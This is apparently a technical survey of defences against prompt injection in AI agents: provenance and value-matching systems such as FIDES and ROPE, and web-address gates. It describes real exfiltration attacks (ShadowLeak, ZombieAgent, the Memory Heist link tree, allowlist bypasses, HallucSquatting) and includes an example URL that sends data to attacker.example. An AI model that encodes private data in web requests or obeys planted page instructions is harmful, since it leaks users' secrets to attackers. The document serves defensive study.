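4. If the planner needs to know something about the hidden text, it sends a question to the quarantined model. The software forces the answer into a fixed format.
5. Before any consequential call, a policy engine compares the labels with the policy for that tool and either runs the call or blocks it.

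For checking references, the fixed format in step 4 could limit the quarantined model to three answers: "supports", "partly supports" and "does not support". FIDES records the type of each value in its label, so a policy can let such a narrow answer into the planner's context without letting in the page. An instruction on the page could still make the quarantined model pick the wrong verdict, but it couldn't put an address or a new task into the answer. The agent would still be allowed to email the co-authors.

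Costa and colleagues also define which tasks need this second model. A task is data-independent if the same sequence of tool calls and the same final response are correct whatever the tools return, as when a user asks an agent to forward a file without reading it. A planner that only passes sealed variables can do such tasks. Reference checking is data-dependent because the correct verdict depends on the page's contents, so someone or something has to read them.

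On AgentDojo, FIDES with suitable policies stopped every injection attack. Compared with a basic planner under the same kind of enforcement, it completed 8% more tasks on average with GPT-4o and 16% more with OpenAI's o1. When Costa and colleagues switched the policy checks off, practical attacks succeeded against every planner they tested, including FIDES. The check before each call provides the security guarantee, while hiding data mainly preserves the agent's usefulness. The guarantee covers data that flows directly into an action, but not everything an observer might infer from the fact that the agent acted.

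In May 2026 Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) works through an attack on an agent that sorts bug reports. A stranger's report contains an instruction to read a file of secrets and publish it as a comment. The planner reads the report directly, follows the instruction and opens the file, which FIDES allows. But the file's contents are private, so the context becomes private too, and the tool that posts comments accepts only public contexts. FIDES therefore blocks the comment or asks a person to approve it. The defence works even after the model has followed the malicious instruction, which no defence in the previous section could guarantee.

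The release also treats a tool's output as trusted and public if the developer forgets to label it, which is a dangerous default. Microsoft acknowledges this and has asked users whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead. They clearly should for a reader agent, because otherwise the framework would trust every web page that an unlabelled tool fetches.

### ROPE: checking the value instead of the whole context

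ROPE (Routed Origin Policy Enforcement), introduced in August 2026, lets the model read everything, including hostile pages, and drops the requirement that the whole context be trusted. Before a consequential call, it checks whether the values that could do harm, such as the recipient of a payment, appear in a source trusted for the task.

Ma and colleagues recognise three such sources, which they call trust anchors:

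- **T1** is the user's own request, together with identity details that the platform maintains, such as the user's email address.
- **T2** is content from a source that the user named in the request and whose identity the platform has authenticated, such as an email with a verified sender.
- **T3** is the user's own authoritative records, such as the platform's log of past orders.

ROPE treats everything else as text an attacker could have written. A web page or a file's body arrives as a single block that anyone may have edited, so ROPE trusts none of it unless the platform can trace the whole block to an authenticated identity, for instance by a signature. This applies even to files the user has named.

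Setting up ROPE requires a one-time list of the tools that change something or send data out, and of the parameters through which an attacker's value could do harm. In the experiments Claude Opus 4.8 drafted this list from the tools' descriptions and the researchers reviewed it. Each parameter gets a default rule from a small vocabulary:

| Rule | Values it accepts |
|---|---|
| PROMPT | Those found in T1 |
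| SOURCED | Those found in T1 or T2 |
| RECORD | Those found in T1 or T3 |
| CONST, ONEOF | One value, or a short list, fixed from the request |
| EXPLICIT | None, unless the request names the target |
| DEST | Any file path outside folders for credentials and system files, unless the request names one |
| FREE | Anything |

When a task begins, a language model called the router reads the request, the list of parameters and trusted facts about the user's account. It names the sources the user pointed to and changes any default that doesn't suit the task. The router never reads what the tools return, so an instruction planted there can't influence it. The rules then stay fixed, but the collection of trusted text grows as the agent reads.

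During the task, ordinary code files each entry in a tool's output under T2, T3 or neither, using the platform's stamp and ignoring what the entry says. When the agent proposes a call to tool $f$ at step $t$, the code checks the value $x_p$ of every sensitive parameter $p$:

$$\text{allow } f(x) \iff x_p \in \mathrm{Adm}_t\big(\pi_r(f,p)\big) \ \text{ for every sensitive } p$$

Here $\pi_r(f,p)$ is the rule chosen for that parameter in request $r$, and $\mathrm{Adm}_t$ is the set of values the rule accepts at step $t$. For PROMPT, SOURCED and RECORD, a value belongs to the set only if it occurs whole in one of the trusted texts, meaning that no letter, digit or joining character, such as a dot or a hyphen, extends it on either side. For example, a trusted email that mentions `joann@uni.org` doesn't let the agent write to `ann@uni.org`. The check doesn't use a language model.

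In the analyst's case, the default rule for an email's recipients is SOURCED. The corrections address appears only on the page behind reference 14, so ROPE blocks email to it. ROPE allows a co-author's address that appears in her request, even after the agent has read eighty untrusted pages, and so avoids the main fault of the strict rule. But ROPE has no counterpart to the list of permitted readers, so if the recipient is acceptable, it doesn't check whether that person may see the contents.

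Ma and colleagues prove two properties of this design. The first, origin soundness, is that a value found only in text an attacker could write never reaches a parameter governed by one of the three source-based rules. The proof is that every such parameter is on the list, so the code checks it and accepts a value only if it occurs in a text filed under an accepted anchor. If the platform's stamps are truthful, that text came from where its stamp indicates.

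The proof depends on three assumptions: the stamps are truthful, the user's records contain only values of trusted origin, and the list of tools and parameters is complete. The second could fail because the agent itself may write to the records. Ma and colleagues show that it still holds if every value written to a record has passed a rule at least as strict as the rules for later uses of that record.

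The assumption about stamps may be harder to meet than it looks. A verified sender address shows who sent an email, but the proof holds only if that person wrote all of it. If a co-author named in the request forwards a stranger's message, the stranger's words get her stamp. A deployment would have to separate quoted text from her own, and the paper doesn't discuss this case.

The second property, paraphrase invariance, means that rewording an injection cannot change the decision on a given value. The injection is not included in the router's input or the trusted texts, so the formula doesn't depend on its wording. Most of the defences in the previous section failed because they lacked this property. The agent may still propose different calls in response to different wordings, and an attacker can still steer it towards a value that happens to be acceptable.

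### What ROPE achieved in tests

The main test used AgentDyn, a set of 60 tasks in software development, shopping and daily life that often require the agent to change its plan. Combining these tasks with planted instructions gives 560 attack cases. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack, then the percentage of attacks that succeeded. DRIFT, the best of the earlier defences in this test, predicts a plan from the request and uses a language model to judge departures from it.

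| Agent model | No defence | DRIFT | ROPE |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 46.7 / 49.6 | 18.3 / 3.2 | 36.7 / 0.3 |
| GPT-4o | 53.3 / 37.4 | 30.0 / 0.8 | 45.0 / 0.3 |
| Gemini-2.5-Flash | 36.7 / 50.8 | 18.3 / 2.6 | 21.7 / 0.3 |
| Qwen3-235B | 65.0 / 61.8 | 31.7 / 7.1 | 45.0 / 0.2 |

The security result is very strong, with the 0.3% for GPT-4o-mini amounting to two successful attacks. The share of undefended task performance retained varied between models and was only 59% on Gemini-2.5-Flash, compared with the paper's headline figure of "up to 84%". With 60 tasks, the gap between 46.7% and 36.7% is six tasks, so small differences between defences mean little. None of the four agents uses a current leading model, and newer ones would presumably complete more tasks with or without ROPE.

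CaMeL completed no tasks on AgentDyn with any of the four models. Some failure is plausible, because a program written before the agent has read anything is poorly suited to tasks that require replanning. But a competitor ran CaMeL on a test chosen to be hard for fixed plans, so the result is weak evidence of how CaMeL would do on a predictable job such as opening eighty addresses in turn.

Ma and colleagues also ran an adaptive attack, in which a language model rewrote each injection over six rounds against the running defence. It barely affected ROPE, but raised DRIFT's attack success rate on Qwen3-235B from 7.1% to 28.5%. Six rounds is far fewer than the 800 attempts that Nasr and colleagues allowed. The proof matters more than this test because it shows that rewording cannot succeed against any guarded value. Another test spread each attack over several emails, calendar entries and files.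 In that test, 71.0% of attacks succeeded on undefended GPT-4o-mini, and none succeeded against ROPE on any of three models.

On AgentDojo, where requests tend to specify more of the task, between 3.7% and 4.6% of fixed attacks succeeded against ROPE, and its advantage over DRIFT mostly disappeared. The router seems to be worth using when a request leaves values to be found elsewhere. On AgentDyn with GPT-4o-mini, the default rules alone completed 25.0% of tasks with no successful attacks. Adding the router raised completion to 36.7% and attack success from zero to 0.3%.

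That improvement depended on a strong router. Replacing Opus 4.8 with Gemini-3-Flash let 5.8% of attacks through, because the weaker router relaxed 67 rules while Opus relaxed two. Ma and colleagues' optional safeguard discards any change that makes a rule looser than its default. With it, no attack succeeded under any of the cheaper routers, but task completion fell to between 15.0% and 18.3%. An operator who can't afford a strong router would do better to use the default rules without a router.

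### Is opening a web page a read or a write?

ROPE does not check read-only calls, so whether it protects private data depends on how it classifies web requests. A request to open a page can send private data out in the URL, even though it looks read-only.

ROPE counts any tool that sends data out as state-changing. Its published lists of these tools include those for browsing a page, entering text into a page and downloading a file in AgentDyn, and those for fetching a page and posting to one in AgentDojo. Under the SOURCED rule, the web address given to each of these tools is a sensitive parameter, so the whole address must appear in the user's request or in an authenticated message from someone the user named. If an agent adds private data to a permitted address, the resulting address doesn't appear in any trusted text, and ROPE blocks the request.

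This makes ROPE safer than its description of read-only calls suggests, but awkward for an agent that follows citations. If the analyst pastes her eighty references into the request, or a named co-author sends them in the body of a verified email, the agent can open all of them. If they are in an ordinary file, ROPE blocks every one, because appearing in a file doesn't make a URL trusted. The agent also couldn't follow a link from reference 14 to the full paper, or open a result from a web search.

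The router can lift the restriction by marking the address as FREE, the rule for values the user lets a document or web page supply. But FREE accepts any address, including one that would send part of the draft to an attacker. ROPE has no rule between "the user supplied this address" and "any address is allowed", and an agent that checks citations often needs one.

ROPE also doesn't check the text an agent types into a page, because the list for that tool includes only the address. Nor does it check the body of an email. Ma and colleagues accept this because the agent composes such text, which needn't appear in any source, but the agent could still send private text to a permitted page or recipient.

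### Learning the rule, or signing the label

Two papers from October 2026 take provenance in opposite directions. One gives up fixed rules, and the other protects the label itself from tampering.

In *PROVISO*, Yan, Zhang and colleagues (2026) train a separate network to decide whether each action the agent proposes should go ahead before the software runs it. In their example, the user asks the agent to pay account B, but the invoice contains a line redirecting the money to account C. The amount may come from the invoice, but the recipient has to come from the user. PROVISO divides the available text into trusted observations, external observations, the proposed action and an alternative, which is either a refusal or another way to continue. It adds a learned vector to each segment to mark its type. The network then estimates the value of the proposed action and of the alternative, and the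 software carries out the one with the higher score.

The marking resembles the origin signal in the provenance-aware transformer, but it is used in a second model. The network learns from past outcomes, and no code enforces the rule about recipients. PROVISO can therefore consider the harm of refusing a harmless task, which fixed rules do not account for. Its F1, a score from 0 to 100 that combines missed threats and false alarms, was 13.84 points higher than the strongest competing method's on a test of malicious add-ons for agents and 7.07 points higher on a test of unsafe tool calls. But the network also reads the attacker's text, so some wording may shift its score, and the design does not rule this out.

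To defend against prompt injection, PROVISO also needs an environment that can be copied and restored. On AgentDojo, it chose between two complete runs of the task after trying each in such a copy. An analyst can't rehearse her agent's visits to eighty live websites this way, because the servers would receive the requests during the rehearsal.

The other paper, Yocam, Vaidyan and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic AI Defense*, covers disguised text that a tool extracts, such as an instruction hidden in an image. A system that labels text on arrival may miss the instruction because it isn't text yet. The paper proposes decode-time provenance binding, which labels the text when a decoding tool produces it. The trusted layer that runs the tools marks the output, and anything later computed from it, as untrusted. It signs a record of these labels with a secret key and stores it in a ledger that the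 agents can't edit.

Before a critical call, such as sending email or exporting secrets, the layer uses the ledger to trace the call's inputs to their origins. It blocks the call if it finds an invalid signature, an untrusted origin or a missing record. It also blocks the call if untrusted decoded text has entered the agent's context, even when no argument contains that text. A person or a policy can approve a specific value, such as an invoice number read from a scan, and the layer records the approval.

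In a test with 24 hidden instructions, all 24 succeeded without a defence, 15 got past a keyword scanner, and none got past the new mechanism. A plain label tracker without signatures also stopped all 24, so this test shows no advantage for the signatures. They did help when Yocam and colleagues simulated a compromised agent passing data to another machine. The agent could forge a trusted label when signatures were removed, and could reuse a genuine label from an unrelated, harmless value when the ledger was removed. These results demonstrate the design on a small test system, and only three tasks checked its effect on legitimate work.

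Decode-time binding alone isn't enough to protect an agent that reads web pages. As the rule is written, a tool's output is trusted unless the tool is on the list of decoders or one of its inputs was already untrusted. Plain text from an ordinary fetching tool would therefore count as trusted until someone added that tool to the list.

| Design | Where the label is attached | What decides on a call | What the software enforces |
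|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES | To each message and stored variable | Fixed code | The labels must satisfy the tool's policy |
| ROPE | To each entry in a tool's output | Fixed code, using rules that a model chose from trusted input | Each guarded value must occur in an accepted source |
| PROVISO | To each text segment in a separate network's memory | A trained network | The option with the higher score goes ahead, with no fixed rule |
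| Decode-time binding | To a decoding tool's output, in a signed record | Fixed code | No critical call with an untrusted origin, except by recorded approval |

### Labels that spread and values that disappear

Conservative labels tend to spread until they cover everything, a problem often called label creep. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026), which deals with confidentiality, a summary of two private records requires authorisation for both before release. This rule is right if a paraphrase could reveal either record, but an agent that has read fifty records can soon share its output with almost nobody. Microsoft reports the same effect for integrity. In its framework, once an untrusted report enters the context, the rest of the run is untrusted unless the developer removes the report.

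Asking a person to approve each blocked call works poorly for an agent that opens eighty pages. Costa and colleagues warn that such requests lead to fatigue, after which people approve without looking. Hiding the text behind variables works better, but it can cause harm even without an attacker. Ma and colleagues describe such a case with PFI, an earlier defence that replaces untrusted data with placeholders. A user asked an agent to look up a colleague's email address in the inbox and send her some access keys. PFI hid the address, so the planner made one up, and the agent sent the keys to the wrong address.

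Value matching has the opposite weakness. ROPE doesn't follow how the agent arrived at a value, so it refuses legitimate values that the agent has reworded or calculated. In Ma and colleagues' tests without attacks, 96 failed tasks included a call that ROPE had refused, and strict matching was the cause in 10 of them, such as when an event title was phrased differently from the request. Stable identifiers such as email addresses would remove most of these failures because, unlike titles, they can't be correctly written in many different ways.

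Paraphrase can also remove a label altogether. In decode-time binding, the label follows data that passes through the trusted layer. If an agent paraphrases an untrusted instruction and sends it through a channel that the layer doesn't control, the label is lost. Yocam and colleagues limit their guarantee to systems with no such channel.

### When the untrusted page is the only source

Better matching wouldn't prevent most of ROPE's refusals. In 83 of the 96 tasks, the value the user wanted existed only in text that an attacker could have written. For example, one user asked an agent to fetch an electricity bill from a website and pay it. The account number appeared only in the bill, so ROPE refused the payment. It would have refused a fraudulent account number for the same reason.

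Suppose the analyst asks her agent to email the maintainer of each page where it finds an error, using the contact address on the page. A genuine address and an attacker's address would both come from the page and carry the same label, so any rule based on origin must accept or refuse both. All seven successful attacks on AgentDyn across the four models happened when the router chose FREE for a case like this.

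More evidence about the value would help. A publisher could sign its contact details, or the analyst could confirm each address herself. Her confirmation would be much like the recorded approval in decode-time binding. For a request for corrections, it would be simpler for the agent to draft the emails and the analyst to send them.

False statements are harder to deal with because they can do harm without any tool call. In 23 of the 51 fixed attacks that succeeded against ROPE across both test sets, the agent's reply recommended a hotel that a planted instruction had promoted. In another 21, the agent sent harmful content to an acceptable recipient, such as a phishing link in a message to the colleague the user had named. ROPE applied its own rules correctly in both groups. Yocam and colleagues likewise state that their mechanism protects actions but not the text of a summary.

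A record of where each value came from can at least help the analyst investigate a doubtful verdict. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 71 works, distinguishes evidence that supports a conclusion from anything that merely influenced it. A page can change a verdict without justifying it, and a log of tool calls shows only that the agent retrieved the page. For citation checking, a useful record would link each verdict to the passage that supports it and to the exact copy of the page the agent read.

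Wang and colleagues found that few systems report protecting their traces against later alteration, and that no benchmark in their catalogue tests the whole chain from source to conclusion. They followed citations from fifteen starting works and had no independent second coder, so they may have missed some systems or benchmarks.

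## Which web addresses should the agent be allowed to open?

A request for a web page is also a message to the site's owner, since sites commonly record requested addresses in their logs, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out. Suppose a planted instruction leads the analyst's agent to open this address:

`https://attacker.example/collect?data=unpublished-result`

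The site's owner can then read the last part in the log.

In 2025, researchers at the security company Radware showed that hidden text in an email could make ChatGPT leak private data through a web address. They sent the email to an account connected to Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent that searches the web and the user's files and writes a report. When the user asked for a summary of the day's email, the agent put private details such as names and addresses into a web address and opened it. Radware disclosed the attack, known as ShadowLeak, in June 2025, and OpenAI had fixed the vulnerability by early August, according to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*. Radware had seen no sign that real attackers used it.

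ROPE gives a reference checker no rule between allowing only trusted addresses and allowing any address. Three kinds of URL restriction now in use could fill this gap. One allows only sites on a list of permitted domains, one allows only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, and one allows only addresses that an independent web crawler has already recorded.

### What happens without a gate

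In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay (2026) measured how often an agent leaks data when nothing checks its requests. They ran a small open model, Qwen2.5-7B, on their own machines. The user always asked for a summary of a page. The application fetched the page and put its title, description and text into the model's context, which also held a secret such as an API key (a password that lets a program use an online service).

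Each hostile page carried an instruction in one of four places: the title, the description, the body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through a chain of redirects. The instruction was to send the secret either in a single request or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The attacker's server received a request in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). In 120 further runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server. In 95% of the successful attacks, the summary that the user saw contained no sign of the attack. A developer who tests an agent by reading its answers would therefore have missed nearly all of these leaks, while a log of outgoing requests would have shown them.

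Splitting the secret cut the attack's success rate from 99% to 77% but made each request look more innocent. The first request contained sensitive data in 26% of these runs, compared with 97% for the single-request attack. The paper also gives 16% for the first three requests together, which is impossible under its own definition because those three include the first, so the sharding figures may be unreliable.

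Lan and colleagues then tried several defences against the simplest version of the attack, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Model attempted the request | Data reached the attacker |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the developer's instructions | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Delimiters around the page | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and delimiters | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| List of permitted domains | 100% | 0% |
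| Block on suspicious-looking addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Block on words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Block on random-looking values | 0% | 0% |

The domain list gives the clearest result. The model followed the page's instructions every time, and ordinary software blocked every request. But this outcome was nearly certain in advance, because the list had only four entries and the attacker's domain was obviously not among them. A list that short would also have blocked nearly all of the analyst's references, an effect the study did not measure.

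The other filters deserve less credit. The block on suspicious addresses looked for words such as "collect" and "steal", which an attacker can avoid. The last two rows are hard to explain, because a filter that inspects finished requests should not change how often the model first attempts one. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids such values when monitoring is active, but this kind of filter would give the model no sign of its presence beforehand.

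They acknowledge that their set-up favours the attacker, because the secret is in plain view and there are almost no developer instructions. The 88% figure is therefore not an estimate for a current commercial agent.

### Lists of permitted domains

A domain list is the oldest and simplest control. The software checks the host name in the proposed address against the list and sends the request only if it finds a match. Anthropic's web fetch tool, for example, lets developers list either permitted domains or blocked ones. An entry for `example.com` also covers `docs.example.com`, and developers can limit an entry to one part of a site.

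If the comparison is correct, the first request can only go to a listed host. The gate does not check the rest of the address, so the address can still carry private data to any site on the list.

The comparison is easy to get wrong. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had a list of documentation sites that it could open without asking the user. Its software checked only whether the host name started with a trusted name, according to Sonatype, a company that tracks software vulnerabilities. An attacker could therefore register a name like this one:

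`modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`

Ownership of a domain name runs from right to left, so this host belongs to whoever owns `example.com`. The flaw has the catalogue number CVE-2026-24052, and Anthropic fixed it in version 1.0.111. A correct check for a trusted domain $d$ and a host $h$ is

$$\text{allow} \iff h = d \ \text{ or } \ h \text{ ends with } \text{"."} + d$$

A lookalike address can get onto the allowlist even if the check is correct, because a Cyrillic "а" looks the same as a Latin "a". Anthropic advises developers to use plain ASCII names where they can.

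A listed site can also redirect the agent to an unlisted one. The server answers a request with a second address, which most software then opens automatically, and a gate that checks only the first address will miss it. According to TechRadar's *Three high-risk AI vulnerabilities discovered in Claude.ai*, the security company Oasis found that any address beginning with `claude.com/redirect/` sent visitors on without checking the destination. Google's advertising system checked only the host name, so an attacker could have bought an advertisement that appeared to lead to Claude.

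The remedy is to stop the agent from following redirects automatically and to check each new address against the allowlist before opening it. This is inconvenient for checking references, because permanent identifiers for journal articles redirect to the publisher's site. The allowlist would need to include both the identifier service and every publisher it might redirect to.

Filtering by domain cannot fix a third weakness, which is that an attacker may have an account on an allowed site. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, allowed outgoing traffic only to certain domains, including Anthropic's own API. Willison (2026), in *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, reports that the security company PromptArmor gave the agent an attacker's API key and had it upload the user's files to the attacker's account. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* had already described a leak through Anthropic's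 API, and the Oasis researchers reused it in their own attack. The same trick could presumably work on any large platform where strangers have accounts, such as a code host or a document-sharing service.

The analyst's software could build her domain list automatically from the hosts in her eighty references. That would stop leaks to unrelated sites, but the list would still include the host of any hostile page she cites. If the page behind reference 14 is hostile, the agent could send her draft to that page's host by including the text in the next address it opens.

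### Addresses that have already appeared

Anthropic's web fetch tool also checks the whole address, and the agent can open only addresses that software has recorded from certain parts of the conversation. When the developer Ayush Paul examined the Claude chat assistant in July 2026, he found that it could open addresses from three places: the user's message, web search results, and links on a page that Claude had already fetched. According to Anthropic's developer documentation, as it stood in June, the tool also accepts addresses returned by the developer's own tools. It rejects any address that Claude writes itself or produces by running code, and any longer than 250 characters.

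This rule blocks the attack at the start of this section. If the agent adds a passage from the draft to an address, the resulting address has never appeared before, so the software doesn't open it. As with ROPE, rewording the page doesn't help the attacker, and the rule needs no list of trusted sites.

Links were the weakness, because whoever writes a page chooses what it links to. *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) showed how links can be used to extract private information one letter at a time. Claude had such information because its memory feature adds a summary of the user's earlier conversations to each new one. The front page of Paul's site linked to one address for each letter. Opening `/a` produced a page with links to `/aa`, `/ab` and so on, and the server generated each of these pages when Claude requested it. Claude followed ten links in a row, and the addresses in the log spelled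 out Paul's name.

Claude never composed an address, so every request satisfied the rule. The information was in the choice of links.

Paul still had to persuade Claude to cooperate. Plain injections and several cover stories failed. He succeeded with a false notice that the network company Cloudflare required AI visitors to identify their users, and obtained his own name, employer and home town. Willison (2026) notes in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that the site also used cloaking, showing the notice only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. This demonstration by one researcher on his own account proves that the leak was possible, but not how often a stranger's page would have succeeded.

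Anthropic closed the hole by stopping the tool from following links it finds on fetched pages. It told Paul it had already identified the problem internally, and it paid him no bounty. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* (2026) describes the change as a fix "for now". That seems fair, because the change removes something people use. A reference often leads to a summary page with a link to the full paper, or to a news article with a link to the report it discusses. The agent can still search for the paper's title, but it can open the paper only if the search returns its address. The accounts of the fix concern the chat assistant, so a developer who uses the tool through the API should check which rule applies there.

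Search results remain a possible channel, because an attacker could publish a set of pages, wait for the search engine to find them, and get the agent to search for one page or another. This would be much harder than generating links on request, since the pages would have to exist beforehand and rank highly enough to appear.

### Addresses that a crawler already knows

OpenAI adopted its present rule after an earlier one failed. Following ShadowLeak, it let ChatGPT open addresses only exactly as provided. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email that got around this by including a separate ready-made address for every letter and digit. ChatGPT spelled out the private data by opening these addresses one after another. Radware reported the attack in September 2025, and OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December.

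In January 2026 OpenAI published a stricter rule, which works as follows:

1. A crawler explores the public web and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to anybody's conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When the agent is about to open an address automatically, software looks for that exact address in the crawler's record.
3. If the address is there, the agent opens it.
4. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation.

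The reasoning is that an address that was already public independently of the conversation is unlikely to contain the user's secrets. OpenAI considered lists of allowed domains too weak because of redirects, and too annoying because people visit far more than a few well-known sites.

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) calls the mechanism Safe Url and uses it as a second layer of defence after the model's own training. Most attacks OpenAI knows of fail because the model refuses. But one 2025 email attack, which closely resembles ShadowLeak, worked in 50% of OpenAI's tests, so the second layer is useful. Safe Url covers page visits in Deep Research and in Atlas, OpenAI's browser. A similar Google check in Chrome restricts the addresses its model generates to known, public ones.

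OpenAI claims only that the gate prevents quiet leaks through the address itself. A page that passes may still be false or contain instructions. The gate also can't detect when an agent spells out data by opening public pages that each stand for a letter or digit. The security researcher Johann Rehberger describes this weakness in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, and says that OpenAI's own technical paper acknowledges it. Anyone with a fairly large blog probably already has the 36 indexed pages needed.

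The rule makes Paul's method impractical. Each of his pages had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so ten levels would require about $27^{10}$, or 200 trillion, recorded addresses. An attacker has to reuse a smaller set of addresses.

The public-index rule is probably the best of the three for reference checking. Most published sources are on pages that a crawler can find, and the rule lets the agent follow links between them. It doesn't cover internal documents, very new pages, or library databases that create a different address for each visit. Rehberger believes ChatGPT treats any address the user types as safe for that session, which would let the agent open any of these that the analyst pastes in herself.

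### Requests that bypass the gate

A URL check can block only the requests that pass through it. Rehberger found that OpenAI had left its earlier check out of the macOS and iOS apps, and requests can also come from software that the agent's developer doesn't control.

When a message contains a link, messaging apps such as Telegram and Slack fetch the page to preview its title and a picture. If a planted instruction makes the agent write a link to the attacker's site with private data in it, the app sends that data to the attacker as soon as the message arrives. The user doesn't have to click, and the agent never calls its web tool. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, a personal agent that people often use through messaging apps, was exposed to this attack with its default Telegram settings. A single setting turns the previews off. Slack has an equivalent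 option, which Willison (2024) publicised in August 2024, so the problem was known before OpenClaw.

The developer can also run every link and image in the agent's output through the same gate before anything displays them. For the analyst, this would include the links in emails to her co-authors.

Giving the agent a terminal creates a larger gap, because coding agents often download files by running a command, and restrictions on the web tool don't apply to that command. The restriction then has to be applied to the network connection that all the agent's programs share.

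### Addresses that a model invents

A stranger may register an invented address deliberately, an attack that Spira, Cohen and colleagues (2026) call adversarial HalluSquatting in *Beware of Agentic Botnets*. They studied downloads of software projects from GitHub and of skills, which are add-ons for personal agents.

A user who asks for a project usually gives only its name, but its GitHub address also includes the owner's name. A model that guesses the owner instead of looking it up may get it wrong. Different models tend to make the same wrong guesses, so an attacker can query a few models about a popular new project, register the most common wrong address and put hostile instructions there.

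The researchers asked six models about well-known projects from 2013 to 2018 and recent projects that were popular at the time. For the recent projects, the models invented the owner 92% of the time. This is presumably a share of answers, since the comparison covered only ten recent projects. The highest rate for downloading a project is 85% in the paper's abstract, but 100% for some combinations of project and model in its introduction. For installing skills, the highest rate was 100%.

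Complete attacks also worked on real products. The coding tool Windsurf fetched the researchers' project in all 20 attempts and followed its instructions in 13. Cursor, running Claude Sonnet 4.5, fetched it in 7 of 20 attempts and followed its instructions in 5. The share of attempts that succeeded from start to finish ranged from 20% to 65% across the coding tools and from 40% to 100% across three personal agents, including OpenClaw.

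These ranges are rough because each result comes from only 10 or 20 attempts. Seven successes in 20, for instance, are compatible with a true rate from about 15% to 59%. The researchers also chose recent and popular projects, which makes attacks easier, so the danger is probably lower for older projects. Their study of prompts and attacks on coding tools centred on one project.

A domain list that contains GitHub allows such an address. Anthropic's rule blocks it because the address comes from the model, so the agent has to search for the project. OpenAI's rule blocks it only until the crawler finds the stranger's page.

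None of this helps if the invented address is already in the analyst's reference list. Once she pastes the list into her request, the address comes from the user, and both Anthropic's and OpenAI's rules allow it. The list therefore needs a separate check. Software could look up each address in a search index and mark any that the index doesn't contain, or that it first recorded after she wrote the draft. A genuine but obscure page might fail this check too, so she should check any marked address herself.

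The table compares the gates on addresses that her agent might propose:

| Proposed address | Domain list | Anthropic's rule after the July 2026 fix | OpenAI's rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| A reference that the analyst pasted | Opens if the host is listed | Opens | Opens |
| A link from a fetched page to a published paper | Opens if the host is listed | Opens only if a search also returns it | Opens if the crawler has recorded it |
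| An address to which the agent has added private text | Opens if the host is listed | Refuses | Refuses or warns |
| One of 36 prepared pages on an attacker's site | Refuses unless the host is listed | Opens only if a search returns it | Opens if the crawler has recorded it |
| An address that the model invented and a stranger registered | Opens if the host is listed | Opens only if a search returns it | Opens if the crawler has recorded it |

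### How much can leak through permitted addresses?

When an agent may open any of $k$ addresses on an attacker's site, its choice can tell the attacker up to $\log_2 k$ bits. One bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. With 36 addresses, for the letters and digits, each choice carries up to 5.17 bits, and $n$ choices carry up to $n \log_2 k$. Twenty choices therefore carry

$$20 \times \log_2 36 \approx 103 \text{ bits}$$

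Rehberger proposes preventing the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. This leaves 36 possibilities for the first choice, 35 for the second and so on. If the order of the requests is hidden as well, for instance because they arrive scrambled, the attacker learns only which 20 of the 36 pages the agent opened:

| Repeat visits | What the attacker sees | Possible messages | Maximum leak |
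|---|---|---|---|
| Allowed | Pages and their order | $36^{20}$ | 103 bits |
| Forbidden | Pages and their order | $36!/16!$ | 94 bits |
| Forbidden | Only which pages | $\binom{36}{20}$ | 33 bits |

A four-digit PIN takes about 13 bits and a date of birth within the past century about 15, so even the smallest figure is enough for both. A 16-digit card number takes at most 53 bits. A random 128-bit key would exceed all three figures.

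The figures are upper limits, and a real agent would leak less. Encoding a message in an unordered set of pages takes a calculation that a language model would probably get wrong. If the agent instead spelled out words using one page per letter, a ban on repeats would stop it from using any letter twice, which rules out most names. Forbidding repeats therefore seems to reduce leaks by far more than the small calculated drop from 103 to 94 bits.

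An attacker can recover the missing letters by preparing more pages. Radware made numbered copies of each address, so that one page meant "a in first place" and another "a in second place". A 20-character string with 36 possible characters in each position needs 720 pages. The agent still opens each page at most once, but the attacker can work out the order from the numbers and so receives all 103 bits. Under OpenAI's rule, the attacker must get all 720 pages into the crawler's record, which is more work than 36 but still possible.

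Paul's site would have got around a ban on repeats without any such preparation, because every address in the sequence was new. Each address also contained all the letters revealed so far, so the last request alone gave away the whole name. Choosing one of 27 links at each of ten steps could transmit up to 48 bits.

### What do limits, caching and warnings cost?

A cap on the number of fetches reduces $n$ directly. Anthropic's tool lets developers set a cap but has none by default. A cap of five fetches among 36 addresses limits the leak to 26 bits, but the attacker can compensate by offering more choices at each step. For example, if a page had a separate link for each of 1,000 towns, one click would reveal the user's home town.

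An overall cap on fetches is little use to the analyst because her agent needs at least 80, and 80 free choices among 36 addresses could leak more than 400 bits. A separate cap for each site would work better. If her list has one reference on a site, the agent can open only that address there. Allowing one extra fetch, so that the agent can follow a link to the full paper, would leak about 5 bits if the page offered 36 links. That seems acceptable, although an attacker with several sites could collect a few bits from each.

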